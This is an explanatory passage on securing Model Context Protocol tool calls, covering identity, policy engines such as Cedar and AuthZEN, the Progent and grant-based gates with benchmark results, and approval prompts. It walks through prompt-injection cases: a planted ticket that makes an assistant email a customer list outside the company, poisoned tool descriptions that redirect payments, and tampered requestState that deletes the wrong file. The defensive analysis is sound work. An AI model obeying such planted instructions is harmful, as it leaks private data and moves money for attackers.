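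*Why MCP security is different*, an article on a security consultant's site, makes the stronger claim that a server has no way to identify the user who initiated a request. This is accurate for a server that holds one shared credential and accepts calls from anybody, but it goes too far for a server that validates each user's access token.

Agents are harder to identify than users. A client can identify itself to the authorization server with the web address of a document that describes it, which proves that someone controls that web domain. But if the application runs on the user's own machine, the document can't prove which local program will receive the login response. The Model Context Protocol's security guidance explains that an attacker's program can present the real client's document, so the user sees the real client's name on the consent page.

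Norman Hardy's 1988 paper "The Confused Deputy" is the classic account of what goes wrong when a program doesn't keep these identities separate. A deputy is a program with authority that its callers may lack. It becomes confused when someone without that authority gets the program to use it for them. Whoever wrote the planted ticket can't read the customer list, but the assistant can, and the writer uses the ticket to make it do so.

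MCP's security guidance uses the term "confused deputy" for a narrower case, in which an MCP server connects many clients to one outside service. The MCP server uses a single client ID with that service, so once a user has consented, the service may skip the consent page next time. An attacker can then register a new client with the MCP server and send the user a login link. If the user clicks it, the attacker's client gains access the user never approved. To prevent this, the MCP server must keep its own record of which clients each user has approved and check it before contacting the outside service. The guidance also forbids servers from passing a client's token to the outside service unchanged, partly because the service's logs may then show the wrong source for the request.

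A large study suggests that many servers don't distinguish between callers. Huang, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile*, examined 6,137 MCP servers, 2,421 of them written in Python and the rest in JavaScript or TypeScript. Their analysis program located where a `tools/call` message triggers a server's own code. It then followed the possible paths from there to sensitive operations, such as running a command or reading a file, and looked for an authorization check specific to the caller. When it couldn't tell from the code whether there was such a check, the program ran the server and sent it test calls.

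The researchers classed 2,846 servers, or 46.4%, as insecure. Their breakdown by category adds up to 1,279 servers with no check, 242 that checked once and reused the stored result, and 1,639 that made checks while running but relied on remembered state or covered only part of what the server could do. These groups overlap. The breakdown also lists 2,554 secure servers, leaving 737 of the 6,137 without a verdict. Excluding those, the insecure share is closer to 53%. In a sample of 100 projects, the program missed between 7% and 10% of authorization cases, and a missed check can make a secure server look insecure.

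An attacker can exploit a server rated insecure only if they can send calls to it after a legitimate user has authorized it. A local server that communicates only with the host that started it is hard to reach this way, which is why MCP's guidance recommends that arrangement. A smaller check by the same researchers, of 87 popular MCP projects with more than 1,000 GitHub stars each, gives a better idea of the practical danger. Eight had authentication flaws that could let attackers run commands on the server remotely.

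Huang and colleagues describe a server for the messaging service Slack that logs in once with a powerful credential and uses it for every later call. Anyone who can reach the server can read and post messages, and Slack cannot distinguish these calls from legitimate ones. The July rule against inferring identity from earlier requests doesn't fix this, because a server can load its credential at startup and never check who is calling. A gateway that authenticates every caller would keep unauthorized callers out if nobody can reach the server directly. But Slack's records would still attribute every call to one account, so the gateway itself has to log which user and agent made each call.

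### The name in a call and the resource it opens

Arguments contain names, and the server determines what each name refers to. The planted ticket might contain an instruction to email `partners@company.example`, a mailing list with members outside the company. A rule that allows email within the company would allow this address, and the mail system would then deliver the customer list to every member. To apply the rule properly, the gate needs the mailing list's membership, which is stored in the mail system.

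Such indirect names are more common now that sessions are gone. The Model Context Protocol suggests that a server that has to remember something between calls return a handle, a short identifier that the model passes back as an argument. A mail server might offer `create_draft`, which returns a handle such as `draft_7f3`, and `send_draft`, which takes only the handle. A gate that checks only the `send_draft` call can't see the recipient. To find it, the gate needs a record of the earlier call or has to query the mail server for the draft's contents.

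Under MCP's guidance, a handle is a name that confers no permission, so the server should check on every call that the draft belongs to the caller. Otherwise anyone who obtains or guesses `draft_7f3` could send or change another user's email. The guidance recommends storing each draft under both its handle and the user ID from the verified token, so that a request from a different user fails even with the right handle.

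A web address, like the file in Garfinkel's example, can lead somewhere different between the check and the use. Model Context Protocol describes how an attacker's domain can lead to a harmless machine when the software checks it and to a machine on the company's internal network a moment later. A harmless address can also redirect to a forbidden one. The guidance suggests reusing the result of the first lookup for the actual connection and checking every redirect. It also advises against writing custom tests for numerical addresses, because attackers exploit unusual notations that such tests often miss.

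Where possible, a gate should resolve the name first, check the resource it refers to, and pass on the resolved form. In the mailing-list case, it could replace the list with its members' addresses and check each one. This fails if the server reinterprets the name in its own way. In that case, the server or the system behind it, whichever opens the resource, should enforce any rule that depends on the interpretation.

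Tool names need the same care because they are unique only within one server. Two servers may each offer a tool called `search`, one for public help pages and the other for customer records. A policy that allows `search` without naming the server would allow both. Gateways that combine several servers SHOULD distinguish the tools, for instance by adding a server identifier to each name. They shouldn't use the name a server reports for itself as the identifier, since two servers can report the same one. The server's address in the gateway's configuration is a better choice.

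### Annotations: what a server claims about its tools

A gate may have a tool's name but no information about what the tool does. Servers can help by attaching annotations to their tool definitions. MCP has had four yes-or-no hints of this kind since March 2025, and a Model Context Protocol post reviewed them about a year later.

| Hint | Meaning when true | Default |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool doesn't modify anything | False |
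| `destructiveHint` | Its changes may destroy something, beyond simply adding to it | True |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments is safe | False |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside people or systems | True |

The defaults are deliberately cautious, so a client should assume that a tool without annotations makes changes, may destroy data, is unsafe to repeat and reaches the outside world. Many servers supply no annotations, and clients differ in how strictly they apply the defaults.

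Clients must treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. A malicious server can mark a tool as read-only and delete the user's files anyway. During the original review, Spahr-Summers asked how a client could use a flag it couldn't trust, and another reviewer, Basil Hosmer, argued that clients should ignore annotations from untrusted servers. The compromise was to call all annotations hints and let each client decide how much weight to give them.

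A gate can let any server's tool annotations make it stricter, but only a trusted server's annotations should make it more lenient. This is slightly better than ignoring unknown servers' annotations, because if an unknown server falsely marks a tool as destructive, the user gets an unnecessary warning, but if it falsely marks a tool as read-only, a gate that relies on the annotation may skip a check that was needed.

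Even honest annotations can mislead. `send_email` adds a message and deletes nothing, so its developer could reasonably set `destructiveHint` to false. A gate that asks for confirmation only before destructive actions would then let the agent email the customer list without confirmation. The ticket server's developer might set `openWorldHint` to false because the ticket database is on the company's own network, even though outsiders write the tickets and one ticket contains the planted instruction. The post recommends treating anything that a tool treats as external as a possible source of untrusted content, but the ticket server's developer may not have considered the tickets external.

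Few products made much use of annotations when the maintainers reviewed them. No MCP client let users filter tools by annotation or showed annotations in its approval prompts. The nearest equivalent in use was the read-only mode of GitHub's MCP server, which about 17% of users had switched on. A read-only mode is blunt but effective for someone who only wants an agent to look things up. The support assistant couldn't use one for its mail server because it has to send the summary.

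Annotations also describe a tool as a whole, while the risk often lies in the arguments. The email to the manager and the email to `outside.example` have the same hints. SEP-1862, "Tool Resolution (preflight checks)", is a proposal that addresses checks before a particular call runs. The Model Context Protocol interest group on annotations lists it as a draft and has not yet decided whether MCP should have annotations that change from one call to the next. More specific information from the server could help a gate distinguish reading a file from overwriting it when one tool does both, but it would still be the server's own claim, and the same rule about trust would have to apply.

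### Tool descriptions that mislead the model or change later

A tool's description reaches the model as text, so it can carry a prompt injection, as a ticket can. The description is more convenient for an attacker because the host may give it to the model in every conversation, before any tool has run. The injection can work without the model calling that tool, as it did with the time-zone server that redirected payments.

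A gate that inspects only `tools/call` messages cannot find such text, because the call contains the tool's name and arguments but not the description that the model read. In the time-zone case, the gate would receive a well-formed call to the payment server, with the attacker's account in the right field. It might catch the unfamiliar account, but to find the cause it would have to inspect the replies to `tools/list`, which contain the descriptions.

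Reviewing the descriptions once, when a user adds the server, is not enough. *Why MCP security is different* points out that the operator of a remote server can change them at will, or on a timer, without any action by the user. With a local server, the user has to install an update first, which gives her a chance to review the change, though few people do. MCP has a notification for changes to the tool list, but it only advises servers to send it, and a malicious server can leave it out.

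Companies that scan servers for suspicious descriptions can still miss them, because a server can tailor its tool list to the caller's credentials. A dishonest server could show the scanner a clean list and employees a different one. The scan should therefore cover the lists that employees' clients receive, and a gateway is well placed to do this because those lists pass through it.

The usual remedy is to pin each definition. When someone approves a tool, the host or gateway stores a hash of its definition, as *MCP-38* recommends, and checks it each time the tool list arrives. If the hash has changed, the gate leaves the tool out of the list and refuses calls to it until someone reviews the change. The gateway needs to control the list as well as the calls because a `tools/call` message doesn't show which version of the definition the model read.

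The hash should cover the entire tool definition, including the input schema. The schema can contain argument descriptions, which the model also reads, and changing it can be harmful. If a weather tool adds a text field called `context` and asks for the recent conversation, the model may send private information in an otherwise ordinary call. The hash should also cover annotations, since a tool newly marked "read-only" might bypass a confirmation prompt.

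Pinning blocks a tool whenever its description changes, even if the developer reworded it for a harmless reason, and the tool stays blocked until a reviewer responds. With thousands of tools, reviewers may start approving changes without reading them. A gateway can reduce the burden by showing reviewers only the altered text and by blocking only the changed tool, so that the server's other tools keep working. Automatically exempting "minor" edits would be risky, because an attacker may need to add only one sentence.

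A schema can also refer to another document by its web address. That document can change without changing the address or the hash. Model Context Protocol forbids implementations from fetching such documents automatically, and allows them to offer fetching only as an option that is off by default. A gateway with that option enabled should store the fetched text and include it in the hash, or refuse any tool whose definition depends on such a document.

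## Deciding by rules: who may do what to which resource

Once a gate knows which parts of a call it can trust, it needs rules that turn them into a verdict. Most access-control systems treat the verdict as a function of four inputs:

```text
decide(principal, action, resource, context) = allow or refuse
```

The principal is the authenticated person or program on whose authority the agent makes the call. The action is usually the tool's name. The resource is the thing the call acts on, such as a ticket or an email address. The context is anything else that matters to the decision, such as the time, the agent in use or whether someone has approved the call. For the email that the planted ticket prompted, the principal is the support employee, the action is `send_email`, the resource is the address `records@outside.example`, and the context includes the assistant's identity.

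A policy doesn't have to use all of these inputs. Using more of them lets it separate wanted calls from unwanted ones more precisely, but someone has to supply and maintain more facts.

### From a list of tools to conditions on arguments

The simplest policy is an allowlist, which checks only the action. The support assistant may call `read_tickets` and `send_email`, and the gate refuses everything else. This prevents the planted ticket from getting the assistant to read the customer list through `read_customers`, but the gate still allows every email.

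With role-based access control, the decision also depends on the principal. An administrator gives permissions to roles, such as "support staff" or "finance", and then gives each person or agent one or more roles. New employees get the right permissions when they join a role. This works well if everyone in a role needs the same access, but badly if access depends on the record. If employees may read only the tickets from their own region, the administrator needs a separate role for each region, and soon for each combination of region and product.

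Attribute-based access control avoids this by comparing facts about the principal, the resource and the context. AWS's guidance page *AGENTSEC02-BP01 Implement tool authorization* gives the example of a clinician who can reschedule appointments only for patients in her own panel. One rule covers every clinician, because it compares the clinician's identity with that of the clinician on the patient's record. Michael Schwartz, who runs the identity software company Gluu, argues that agents need rules of this kind. In a talk reported in Biometric Update's *AI agent delegation via MCP has gaps a Murderbot could walk through*, he pointed out that access may depend on facts unrelated to the agent, such as a data-sharing agreement between two organisations.

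The gate often has to identify the resource from a tool call's arguments. *MCP authorization standards* (Olivier, 2026) explains that the scopes in an access token are therefore not enough, because the login service sets them when it issues the token, before the model has chosen any arguments. A company that tried to write every rule about individual records as a scope would end up with either a few scopes that are too broad to be safe or thousands that nobody could manage. Olivier co-founded Cerbos, which sells a policy engine, so he has a commercial interest in this argument, but it is correct.

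He also claims that a token has no standard place for the user an agent acts for. This is less convincing for a single agent, because a draft standard he co-wrote takes the user's identity from one field of the token and the agent's from another. The claim is stronger for a chain of agents, where the last token may no longer identify the person who started the work.

When a token identifies both the user and the agent, the policy should usually require that both have permission. If the gate checks only the agent, an employee can use an assistant with broad access to read records that she couldn't open herself. An experimental agent can also do everything its user can if the gate checks only the user.

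### The grant test

Liu (2026), in *From Tool Connection to Execution Control*, states a compact test for a single call, based on recorded permissions called grants. In outline:

```text
Allow principal p to perform action a on resource r at time t only if:

  1. one grant exists that
       - is active at time t,
       - names p as its principal,
       - covers a and every scope that a requires, and
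       - covers r; and

  2. if a requires approval, a person has approved this call.
```

All the details must match within one grant. An expired grant to email the auditor and a current grant to email the manager don't together give permission to email the auditor.

The permission check has to use the resource the call will actually open. In Liu's design, trusted code next to the tool determines which resource that is, and the caller's own description can't override the result.

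Approval is a separate condition, and it can't replace a missing grant. Suppose the assistant shows the user a prompt about the email to `outside.example`, and she clicks "yes" without reading the address. The gate still refuses the call, because no grant covers that address. This protects the company from a careless click, but a user with a good reason for an exception has to find someone with the authority to add a grant.

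The OpenID Foundation, which maintains widely used login standards, applies the same principle in a draft for handling approvals. In the draft's example (OpenID Foundation, 2026), an agent tries to pay a supplier more than a set limit. The decision point responds that the payment needs approval, and a manager approves it through the company's normal process. The decision point then evaluates the policy again, with the approval as one of its inputs. If someone has meanwhile withdrawn the agent's permission to make payments, the decision point denies the payment despite the approval.

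Grants also handle delegation better than an ownership check. If an employee covers a colleague's tickets during a holiday, a server that lets people open only their own tickets will refuse her. A server that checks grants will let her open them if an administrator has given her a grant for those tickets, which can be set to expire when the holiday ends.

### A policy for the email example

Cedar is a language for writing access policies, and AWS uses it in the gateway it sells for agents. According to AWS, the gateway refuses every call that no rule permits, and a rule forbidding a call always overrides one permitting it. Schwartz favours Cedar because its policies are "analyzable", meaning that software can check a policy's properties before anyone relies on it. For example, an administrator could check whether any combination of rules lets a temporary worker email people outside the company.

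A short Cedar policy for the support team might look like this:

```cedar
// 1. Support staff may email colleagues.
permit (
  principal in Role::"support-staff",
  action == Action::"send_email",
  resource
)
when { resource.domain == "company.example" };

// 2. Support staff may email the outside auditor.
permit (
  principal in Role::"support-staff",
  action == Action::"send_email",
  resource == Address::"reviews@auditor.example"
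);

// 3. Email to any outside address needs approval.
forbid (
  principal,
  action == Action::"send_email",
  resource
)
when { resource.domain != "company.example" }
unless { context.approved };
```

The first two rules work as grants, and the third adds the approval condition. The enforcement point sets `approved` to true only if a trusted approval system has recorded a person's consent to this call. Three calls from a member of the support staff then get these verdicts:

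| Recipient | Rule that permits it | Does rule 3 forbid it? | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| `manager@company.example` | Rule 1 | No, the address is inside the company | Allow |
| `records@outside.example` | None | Yes, unless someone approves | Refuse, even with approval |
| `reviews@auditor.example` | Rule 2 | Yes, unless someone approves | Refuse until someone approves, then allow |

The policy works only if the gate extracts the recipient correctly. If the gate only tested whether the `to` argument ended in `@company.example`, an attacker could put two addresses in the field, with the outside one first, and the mail server might send the email to both. A safer gate splits the field into separate addresses, finds the domain of each and applies the policy to every address.

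The policy also doesn't restrict the body of the email. If the planted ticket led the assistant to send the customer list to a colleague who has no right to see it, rule 1 would allow that. So the policy is fairly good at keeping email inside the company, but it can't determine which colleague should receive what.

### A common format for requesting a verdict

If a company buys its gateway and its policy engine from different suppliers, the two need a common format. The OpenID Foundation's AuthZEN working group wrote the Authorization API to provide one. An enforcement point sends a subject (AuthZEN's word for the principal), an action, a resource and a context, and the decision point returns a verdict. The OpenID Foundation's *Authorization API 1.0 Final Specification Approved* (2026) announced in January that members had approved the final text by 81 votes to 1, with 25 abstentions.

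The API doesn't specify how to turn an MCP call into those four parts. A second AuthZEN project, called COAZ (for "Compatible with OpenID AuthZEN"), deals with that. In the first draft, from February 2026, Tulshibagwale and Olivier (2026), in *AuthZen Profile for Model Context Protocol Tool Authorization*, have each server include a mapping in the input schema of its tools. The mapping consists of short expressions that pick values out of the call's arguments and the access token. For `send_email`, it could take the subject from the token, the resource from the `to` argument and the agent's identity from the token. The gateway would then send the decision point this request:

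```json
{
  "subject":  { "type": "user", "id": "alice@company.example" },
  "action":   { "name": "send_email" },
  "resource": { "type": "address", "id": "records@outside.example" },
  "context":  { "agent": "https://company.example/support-assistant" }
}
```

Some calls need more than one permission. A tool that copies a file must read from one location and write to another, so its mapping can list two actions and two resources, and the gateway requests a verdict on each pair.

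At least one part of the subject must come from the token, so the model can't claim to act for another user by writing a different name in an argument. Other parts can come from the arguments. In one of the draft's examples, the context includes a case number that the caller supplies. The policy should treat this number as an unverified claim unless the decision point can look up the case.

The server's developers write the mapping, which is convenient because they know what each argument means. But this gives them influence over how calls to their own server are checked. If the mail server's mapping named the sender's mailbox as the resource and left out the recipient, the decision point could not check who the message was going to. A company should therefore review the mapping when it approves a tool, and write its own for servers it doesn't trust. Because the mapping is part of the input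 schema, comparing hashes of the full tool definition will reveal any later change to it.

The draft has also drawn criticism from inside the working group. In March, *Updated COAZ proposal* (Auto De Medeiros, 2026) observed that the draft covers only tool calls and doesn't set the standard names some members wanted for MCP's actions and resource types. Without standard names, two servers might describe the same kind of resource differently, and an administrator would have to write two rules for it.

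The working group adopted COAZ as an official draft in June. On 31 July, *Getting Cozy with COAZ* (Tulshibagwale and Olivier, 2026) announced that the group had split the draft into a general framework and a binding for MCP. The binding has a fixed default mapping for each MCP method, so a gateway can request a verdict on tools whose developers wrote no mapping. Both documents are still drafts, and each must pass through an "Implementer's Draft" stage before the foundation can ratify a final version. The mapping expressions in the July announcement are written differently from those in the February draft, so anyone who builds on COAZ now should expect to revise the work.

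### Who writes the policy

Administrators usually write access policies by hand. AWS also lets them describe a rule in ordinary language and generate the Cedar policy from it. Either way, AWS recommends first running the policy in log-only mode on live traffic, and reviewing it every quarter to remove unused permissions.

An administrator writes these rules before anyone knows what users will request. The assistant has to summarise tickets on Monday and email the auditor on Tuesday, so the policy must permit both on both days. On Monday the user does not need the permission to email the auditor, but an attacker could exploit it.

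The alternative is to have software derive a new, narrower policy from each task. The simplest version is a tool filter. Before the agent starts, a language model reads the user's request and lists the tools the task needs, and the host removes the rest. For the ticket summary, the filter would keep `read_tickets` and `send_email`. This is an allowlist for one task, and it has the same weakness as other allowlists, since an agent with access to `send_email` can email anyone.

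Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, add conditions on arguments. Their system, also called Progent, works as follows for the ticket summary.

1. A language model receives the user's request and the list of tools, and writes an initial policy. It does this before the agent has read any tickets, so a planted ticket can't influence it. The policy might allow `read_tickets` when `status` is `open`, and `send_email` when `to` is the manager's address.
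2. Ordinary software compares every tool call with the policy. It checks the rules that forbid calls first, then those that allow them, and blocks any call that matches no rule.
3. After a call, a language model decides whether the result could require a change to the policy. It makes this decision without access to the result. If the answer is yes, it receives the result and proposes a new policy.
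4. A solver, a program that can prove statements in formal logic, compares the new policy with the old one. If the new policy allows nothing that the old one blocked, it takes effect immediately. Otherwise it is an expansion and needs explicit approval.

The comparison in the last step has a simple definition. Let A(P) be the set of all calls that policy P allows. A new policy P′ is a narrowing if

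$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

and an expansion if it isn't. A set like this can be endless, so the solver can't go through it call by call. It looks instead for a counterexample, a single call that P′ allows and P blocks. Suppose the planted ticket misleads the model into proposing a policy that also allows email to `records@outside.example`. An email to that address is a counterexample, so the policy can't take effect without approval. If the model only proposes to restrict `read_tickets` to one ticket number, no counterexample exists and the change is automatic.

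Shi and colleagues call the resulting guarantee monotonic confinement, meaning that the set of calls the agent can make never grows between approvals. Progent's language models can still make mistakes, but a mistake can't give the agent more power than its last approved policy allows. Two earlier systems, Conseca and DRIFT, also have a language model write the policy, but according to Shi and colleagues, neither checks that policy deterministically.

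### How well Progent worked

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark with simulated banking, messaging, travel and office tasks in which attackers plant instructions in the data the agent reads. With gpt-4o used for both the agent and the policies, Progent cut the share of attacks that succeeded from 39.9% to 1.0%. On ASB, another benchmark of planted instructions, it cut the share from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agents completed about as many of the users' tasks as they did without Progent. On AgentDojo, agents with the tool filter completed fewer tasks than agents with Progent, and more attacks succeeded, because the filter could only allow a tool completely or remove it.

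The headline figures are limited evidence about monotonic confinement. In those tests, Progent approved every expansion automatically, to represent a careless user. The solver therefore blocked nothing, and the low rate shows mainly that the model wrote good policies and that planted text seldom led it to write bad ones. The initial policy alone, without updates, reduced the rate on AgentDojo to 2.5%. Refusing all expansions gave the lowest rate of any automatic setting, and having a person review the initial policy and every expansion reduced it to zero.

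Only 6% of policy updates were expansions, so that kind of review might be bearable. But these were benchmark tasks with clear goals, and the reviewers presumably knew they were in a security test. A busy employee with a vague request might approve more than she should.

The baseline attack success rate of 39.9% reflects a model that was easy to mislead. With Claude Sonnet 4, Progent reduced the rate from 6.8% to 0.5%. That is still a large proportional reduction, but there were fewer successful attacks to prevent. There may be even fewer with newer models.

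Shi and colleagues also rebuilt AgentDojo's tools as MCP servers and connected them to several existing agent products. The attack success rate fell to around 1% there too. Progent can run as a proxy, which requires no changes to the agent, but the proxy can't check the agent's built-in tools.

Most of the failures on ASB involved attack tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools. A person would probably struggle to tell them apart without knowing in advance which ones to trust. Hand-written rules reduced the failure rate to zero, as one would expect if the people writing them knew this.

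*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that malicious tool results may lead the update mechanism to relax those policies. The first problem applies to any system of rules, and the solver addresses the second only if someone examines the expansions. Progent also can't stop an attack that stays within the task's legitimate permissions. If a user wants her agent to choose and buy a laptop, a seller can plant text that praises its own product, and the policy will allow the resulting purchase.

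### Testing the grant test

Progent's language model has to predict which calls a task will need. Liu's experiments mostly avoid this prediction because the grants come from the benchmark's own solutions.

Liu wrote two gates that apply the grant test and related checks, such as making each approval valid only once. One, called HCP, keeps grants, tasks and records in a single program. The other, built for comparison, splits an access-control list between a gateway and a server. Their agreement shows that the checks work in both architectures, but neither gate is an independent test of the other, because Liu wrote both and gave them identical grants.

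In the first experiment, a script attempted 18 violations and 25 benign workflows, with no language model involved. Liu also ran weaker setups with connection-level checks, such as whether the caller owns a record and whether the headers match the body.

| Setup | Violations prevented (of 18) | Benign workflows completed (of 25) |
|---|---|---|
| No authorization checks | 0 | 25 |
| Connection checks, operator accepts every approval request | 7 | 24 |
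| Connection checks, operator declines high-risk requests | 14, with 1 unclear | 14 |
| HCP | 18 | 25 |
| Gateway and server access list | 18 | 25 |

The perfect scores are not very impressive, since Liu designed the violations around the properties that the two gates enforce. In the third row, declining every high-risk request blocked 11 of the 25 benign workflows, and three violations still succeeded. Liu also removed HCP's checks one at a time. Removing grant matching let six violations succeed, more than any of the other 15 removals.

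The second experiment used language models on 24 AgentDojo tasks. The grants allowed every read-only tool. For tools that change something, they allowed only the operations and targets in the benchmark's reference solution. One model, gpt-6.1-sol, received planted content in 141 of 144 sessions but never attempted what the attacker wanted, so the gates had no attacks to block. The other, deepseek-v4-pro, achieved four of the attackers' goals without a gate, including a money transfer and a phishing link sent to a colleague. With a gate, it made ten calls aimed at such goals, and the gates blocked all ten. This is good evidence that the gates block what their grants exclude. It isn't enough to estimate how much they reduce attacks overall, because outcomes changed on only three tasks and the difference was not statistically significant.

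Liu then tested three other models on 24 new tasks, with an attacker who could revise the planted text after a failed attempt. None of the models attempted the attacker's goal, with or without a gate.

### The wanted work that narrow grants block

The follow-up is more informative about false stops. In sessions with no attack, the agents completed 68 of 69 tasks without a gate, 60 of 68 with the access list and 59 of 67 with HCP. Completion fell from about 99% to 88% with either gate, so roughly one task in ten failed because of the gate. These figures exclude 12 sessions that reached a limit on turns or calls.

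In the earlier experiment, the gates blocked 40 calls that were unrelated to an attacker's goal. Two of them used a tool that the reference solution didn't use. In the other 38, the agent had chosen a date or time, title, city or channel name that differed from the reference solution's.

Looser matching of date formats, city names and capital letters would not have allowed any of the 241 refused writes that Liu replayed from the two AgentDojo studies. They were among 3,299 recorded calls that Liu replayed to test whether the gates were too strict about format, for example by refusing "3 pm" because the grant specified "15:00". Of the refused writes, 219 differed from the reference solution in substance, 15 used a tool that the solution didn't use, six were unclear and one was equivalent. Allowing all 241 would have let through at least four successful attacks.

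So a better text comparison won't fix the problem. But differing "in substance" here means differing from the benchmark's solution, and a user might be just as happy with a meeting called "Budget review" as with one called "Q3 budget". When the models ran without a gate or an attack, they made 13 writes outside the grants and still completed nearly every task, so some of those writes were probably fine. Liu also warns that refusing a call outside these grants doesn't prove that the call was wrong.

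In practice the losses could be larger, because real administrators don't have a reference solution and so will sometimes leave out a permission that a task needs. The losses could also be smaller, because administrators would rarely write a grant that fixes the exact title of a meeting.

The checks add almost no time. In the first AgentDojo experiment, the median tool call took 0.39 milliseconds without a gate, the same with the access list, and 0.57 with HCP. The median request to gpt-6.1-sol took 4.6 seconds. Copying a file through a real MCP server took 2.28 milliseconds without a gate and about 0.3 milliseconds longer with HCP. Over 1,000 workflows, HCP used 7.7 megabytes of additional memory because it keeps all its records, while the access list used 0.7. All of this ran on one machine, and a gateway elsewhere on the network would add message travel time.

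### Predictable verdicts and their price

The main argument for rules is that the same inputs always produce the same verdict, so an administrator can test a policy before using it and find the rule responsible when a call fails. In Liu's first AgentDojo experiment, the two gates' verdicts matched the rule on all 1,012 calls. Olivier reports that Nathan Harris, an analyst at Gartner, thinks AI can help write policies but the decision on each call must be deterministic.

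Persuasive text also doesn't change the rules. If someone writes in a ticket that the chief executive has authorised the transfer of the customer list, that doesn't add `outside.example` to the list of permitted addresses. A second language model acting as a judge could assess whether an email suits the task, but text planted to mislead the agent might mislead the judge too.

This immunity covers only the comparison between a call and the policy. When a language model writes the policy, two runs of the same task may produce different rules and so different verdicts. An attacker can also steer the agent towards something the rules permit. For example, a rule that let the agent message any colleague, as the first Cedar rule does for email, would not have stopped deepseek-v4-pro from sending the phishing link to a colleague. Liu's gates let a secret pass to a permitted destination as an ordinary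 argument because they checked the destination but did not track the data.

Narrower rules prevent more of this misuse but also block more calls that users want. If the manager is on holiday, the user might ask the assistant to send the summary to "whoever is covering for her". The assistant looks up the deputy's name in the staff calendar and tries to email him. The Cedar policy allows this because he works for the company, but a Progent policy that names only the manager blocks it until someone approves an expansion. Neither policy lets the assistant reply to a customer, which a support team does all day. An administrator could add a rule that permits email to the customer who filed the ticket, but whoever filed the planted ticket would also qualify, so the assistant could send that person the customer list.

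It therefore makes sense to write narrower rules for actions where a mistake would do more harm. Liu's grants allowed all reading and restricted only changes, and Progent's AgentDojo tests also allowed tools that read non-sensitive data. The support assistant would have broad access to open tickets but only a short list of permitted outside recipients. If the gate wrongly refuses an email to the auditor, someone can add a grant and send it an hour later, but nobody can recall a customer list that has reached a stranger.

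## Asking a person to approve the call

Rules written in advance can't settle every call, so a gate can hold the doubtful ones and ask a person. The user of the support assistant, for example, knows she wanted one email to her manager summarizing the open tickets. But her answer helps only if the prompt shows what the call will do and she reads it.

### From one answer to a standing rule

The host usually determines which calls trigger a prompt. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* describes a default under which the coding tool prompted the user before every file write and shell command. Since August 2026, new sessions on most Claude Code subscriptions have used a classifier, a model that evaluates each call, in place of most prompts. A host can also prompt when a tool's annotations mark it as destructive, or when a policy requires approval, as the third Cedar rule does for outside addresses.

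MCP doesn't define the answers a user can give. Hosts offer different sets, usually drawn from these:

| Answer | This call | Later calls |
|---|---|---|
| Allow once | Runs | The next call prompts again |
| Allow for the session | Runs | Matching calls run without a prompt until the host's session ends |
| Always allow | Runs | Matching calls run without a prompt until someone removes the rule |
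| Refuse | Doesn't run | The agent may propose the same call again |
| Always refuse | Doesn't run | The gate refuses matching calls without a prompt |

An "always allow" answer turns one decision into a policy, and its effect depends on what counts as a matching call. Suppose the user chooses it for the summary to her manager. The host could store either of these rules:

```cedar
// Narrow: Alice's assistant may email her manager.
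permit (
  principal == User::"alice@company.example",
  action == Action::"send_email",
  resource == Address::"manager@company.example"
);

// Broad: Alice's assistant may email anyone.
permit (
  principal == User::"alice@company.example",
  action == Action::"send_email",
  resource
);
```

Under the broad rule, the host would later send the customer list to `outside.example` without prompting her, unless a separate rule blocked it. She saw only the email to her manager when she clicked, so the narrow rule is the safer interpretation of her answer.

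Many users end up with broad rules. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that by June, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule allowing some shell commands without a prompt. Many of these rules cover an interpreter such as Python, which can run any program, so these rules allow almost anything. Also, 62% of users had either switched off permission checks at some point or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions began with the checks off.

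Standing permissions can also be hard to find or withdraw. Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, tested five commercial agents in May and June. In Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, they found no way to revoke folder access within a session after granting it. A new session started without the permission, but an old one still had it when they reopened it. In the Claude chatbot, a tool set to "Needs approval" created an email draft without asking, and Claude explained that the request had implied permission. These products change quickly, so the details may be out of date. The researchers also reviewed 21 proposed permission systems, and only six clearly let users change or revoke a permission later.

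### How a server pauses a call

A server may have its own reasons to request approval. For example, the mail server can detect that an address is outside the company, and a database server can detect that a query would delete records. Before July 2026, a server could send the client a question while the original call stayed open. This was awkward for services that run many interchangeable copies of a server, because the answer had to reach the copy that was waiting for it. In the Model Context Protocol's release post, Inian Parameshwaran of the database company Supabase says this is why its server hadn't offered such confirmations.

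The July revision replaced these questions with multi round-trip requests. For the email that the planted ticket prompted, the exchange would go as follows.

1. The client sends the `send_email` call. The mail server finds an outside recipient and holds back the email.
2. The server returns an interim result containing a question and a block of text called `requestState`, in which it stores whatever it needs to resume. It can then forget the call.
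3. The host shows the question to the user and collects her answer.
4. The client repeats the call under a new message number, with the original arguments, her answer and an exact copy of `requestState`.
5. The server checks the state and the answer, then sends the email or refuses.

The interim result in step 2 might look like this:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 4,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "input_required",
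    "inputRequests": {
      "confirm_send": {
        "method": "elicitation/create",
        "params": {
          "mode": "form",
          "message": "Send this email to records@outside.example?",
          "requestedSchema": {
            "type": "object",
            "properties": { "approved": { "type": "boolean" } },
            "required": ["approved"]
          }
        }
      }
    },
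    "requestState": "v1.9f3c..."
  }
}
```

A gateway could return the same kind of result, because the client treats the gateway as the server. But not every client can display the form. Model Context Protocol's *Multi Round-Trip Requests* forbids servers from sending types of question that the client hasn't declared support for. Körbächer (2026), in *Designing requestState for Multi Round-Trip Requests*, recommends cleanly refusing destructive actions in that case. If the client never repeats the call, the server doesn't send the email.

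### Tying the answer to the call

The client holds `requestState` between the two calls, so a compromised client can change it. Körbächer gives the example of a server that stores its progress and a list of files to delete in unprotected text. The client edits the text so that the confirmation appears complete and the list contains a different file. The server then deletes a file that nobody agreed to delete.

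The specification therefore tells servers to treat the returned state as if an attacker had written it, but many of the protections it lists are only recommendations. The table compares these protections with the defaults in MCP's Python software kit, as described in Model Context Protocol's *Multi-round-trip requests*.

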